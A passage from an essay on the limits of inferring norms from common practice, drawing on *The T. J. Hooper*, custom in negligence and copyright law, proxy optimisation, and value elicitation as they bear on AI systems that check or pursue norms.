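Reformers deviate from common practice on purpose. In a society where slavery was normal, a checker that took its values from common practice would flag the people who freed their slaves. *Full-Stack Alignment* (Edelman, Zhi-Xuan and colleagues, 2025) criticises models that record only what people prefer, because they treat the rejection of slavery as an arbitrary change of preference when they have no record of the reasons for it. A count of artifacts has the same defect, since it also leaves out people's reasons.

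Courts face a version of this problem when they decide whether someone who followed a trade's custom took enough care. In March 1928, two tugs were towing coal barges from Virginia to New York when a gale off New Jersey sank two of the barges. The government broadcast weather forecasts twice a day, but the tugs missed them because their captains' private radios weren't working. Only one company on that coast supplied its tugs with radios. In *The T. J. Hooper*, Hand (1932) still found the tugs at fault. He wrote that reasonable prudence is usually common prudence, but that "strictly it is never its measure", since "a whole calling may have unduly lagged" in adopting new devices.

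A checker that went by what most tugs did would have flagged the one company with radios. The judge, Learned Hand, instead considered what a radio was for. It was cheap and fairly reliable, and it warned of dangers that a tug towing half a mile of barges couldn't learn about in any other way.

The ruling is weaker evidence against custom than its famous phrases suggest. Hand found "no custom at all" about radios, because some tugs had them and some didn't, so he didn't need his remark about a whole trade to decide the case. He also relied on other captains' conduct, treating the fact that four other tows had taken shelter that day as unusually good evidence of what impartial experts thought. He recognized that the later captains had partly followed the first one's example, but those who testified had also received a forecast.

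American law mostly takes this middle position. Rothman describes the dominant rule as treating custom as some evidence of reasonable care, but not as the definition of it. Medical malpractice law long relied more heavily on custom. The American Law Institute's *A New Legal Standard for Medical Malpractice* (2025) reports that the institute, a body of lawyers that restates the law for courts, moved away from this in 2024. Its new standard lets juries override a customary practice in some cases when the practice falls short of contemporary standards, though many courts still rely heavily on what doctors usually do.

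A defender of the proposal could add dates to the corpus to show which practices spread. Radios spread from one company to the rest, and a new practice that people keep after trying it is often an improvement. But this evidence is available only after a practice has spread, so it would not have helped the barges in 1928. Some bad ideas also spread just as quickly.

### Customs that people didn't choose freely

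Artifacts also reflect what their makers could afford and what other people allowed. Edelman and colleagues point out that someone who puts work before relationships looks the same whether they do it out of ambition or because of social pressure.

In American copyright law, fair use permits some copying without permission, but nobody can be sure beforehand what a court will accept, and a wrong guess can be very expensive. Rothman argues that people therefore pay for licences they may not need, and courts then treat this habit as a standard. In one case, a court rejected a fair-use defence for a poster shown for less than 30 seconds in the background of a television comedy, because the industry usually licensed such posters. Rulings like this encourage more people to buy licences, which strengthens the custom. An AI system that acted on inferred norms could start a similar loop, because the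 things it made would join the corpus.

Powerful groups also shape customs. Large publishers and a few authors' organisations negotiated the US guidelines on classroom copying, with little or no input from teachers and students. The guidelines were meant to state the minimum that teachers could copy, but courts came to treat it as the maximum.

Epstein (2008), in *Some Reflections on Custom in the IP Universe*, accepts some of Rothman's criticisms but defends custom in a wide range of injury and contract disputes. Rothman reports Epstein's argument that negotiated licences reflect good private arrangements because both sides agreed to the price. She replies that small users often can't find the owner or get an answer in time, and that the public also loses when a work never appears. Her objection is strongest where a custom affects people who had no part in making it, while Epstein's defence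 is more convincing where the same people deal with each other repeatedly, each sometimes buying and sometimes selling.

One way to save the proposal is to screen the norms. Rothman would ask how clear and widespread a custom is, why it arose, whether it represents everyone it affects, and what would happen if it became a rule. Some economists leave out choices that people make under conditions such as addiction. Edelman and colleagues answer that the choices themselves don't show which conditions should disqualify them, so somebody first has to decide what is good for people. Screening can therefore improve the inference, but it brings in some of the values that the artifacts were supposed to supply.

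### What happens when a system pursues a norm

A bug finder only points to existing code, whereas an AI system that pursues a norm looks for new ways to satisfy it. Edelman and colleagues describe how a person's wish for meaningful connection becomes "engagement" in the software that recommends posts, daily users for the company and quarterly revenue for the market. Time spent on a site may be a fair sign of connection while people mostly use it to talk to friends, but software designed to maximise that time can increase it by encouraging compulsive scrolling.

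Searching harder makes this worse. Suppose an option's score is its real worth plus an independent error, and the two have the same distribution. On average, half of any unusually high score is then error. If very large errors are more common than very large real worth, the highest scores are almost entirely error. Someone who compares a few ordinary options rarely encounters such scores, but a powerful optimiser selects for them.

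The system could instead treat norms as limits. It would follow people's instructions while staying close to what people commonly do, as the robot did when it inferred that it shouldn't break the vase. This would steer the system away from the strangest options, but also from improvements such as the first radios on tugboats. The approach wouldn't be completely safe, because a series of common actions can still lead to a very unusual result.

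Edelman and colleagues prefer "thick models of value," which record why something matters to people and how it relates to their other values. Such a model might distinguish friendship from scrolling even when both keep someone online for an hour. They acknowledge that these models are still mostly theoretical.

### Verdicts and questions

Most of these objections are less serious if the tool only asks about deviations. In the invented project where 200 functions kept a lock and 20 of them did so by mistake, a tool that "repaired" all 200 would break 180 working functions, while one that asked the programmers would break none if they answered correctly, though it would need 200 short conversations. Meta's engineers also put up with so many false alarms because the questions are short.

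Liscio and colleagues describe a similar approach to values. In their example, policymakers consult the public about COVID-19 rules on a website, where software estimates each person's values from their comments and votes. The estimate for one participant, Amber, differs noticeably from the group's. Her software assistant checks whether it has misread her behaviour, whether the list of values leaves out something she cares about, and whether the group's values need recalculating, rather than treating the difference as her mistake. It might ask why she voted for a particular comment, and she may still differ from the group at the end.

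Asking people directly has its own problems. Edelman and colleagues warn that after a long conversation with an AI system, it is hard to tell what a user wanted from what the user merely accepted at the system's suggestion. People may also misreport their values to get their way, and how much this matters depends on how the system combines the answers. Suppose nine people choose 0 on a scale and one chooses 10. A rule that minimises the total distance from everyone's choice gives 0, so the minority has no effect. A rule that minimises the distance from the least satisfied person gives 5, which nobody chose. If the tenth person exaggerates and says 20, the second rule gives 10, which is what that person wanted. Liscio and colleagues suggest allowing several answers when people fall into distinct groups.

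A system that questions only the people who deviate also never examines the majority. If asked why it was different, the company with radios could have said that radios give warning of storms. The other companies would have benefited most from that answer, so the system would need to ask them why they had no radios.

### Conflicts between a person's own commitments

Engler and colleagues looked for contradictions in MUST beliefs, and the same approach could work for values. If a company promises to delete records after 30 days but its backup system keeps them for seven years, something is wrong, whatever other companies do. Because this method doesn't depend on how common a practice is, copying doesn't distort the evidence, and a reformer isn't judged wrong for being in the minority.

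The contradiction doesn't show whether the company should change its promise or its practice. It may have forgotten about the backups, or it may have made the promise without noticing that the law requires it to keep the records. English common law partly addressed this kind of conflict. Rothman explains that a custom had to be consistent with other customs in the same community and couldn't contradict the laws of the King or Parliament. Judges therefore knew that statute came before custom, but people rarely rank their own commitments that clearly.

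Many values that seem to conflict are compatible. Someone can value both honesty and tact and give more weight to one or the other depending on the situation, whereas a pointer can't be both null and not null. Edelman and colleagues suggest looking for a broader value, such as respect for the person one is talking to, that explains when each should come first. Finding one takes reflection, and two thoughtful people may find different ones.

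Slavery shows both the strength and the weakness of checking people's commitments for contradictions. A slaveholder who declared that all people are born free held conflicting commitments, and an observer could have pointed this out even if every neighbour owned slaves. Many abolitionists made this argument. But some defenders of slavery removed the conflict by denying that the principle applied to the people they enslaved. This made their position more consistent, so a checker that looked only for contradictions would have stopped reporting it.
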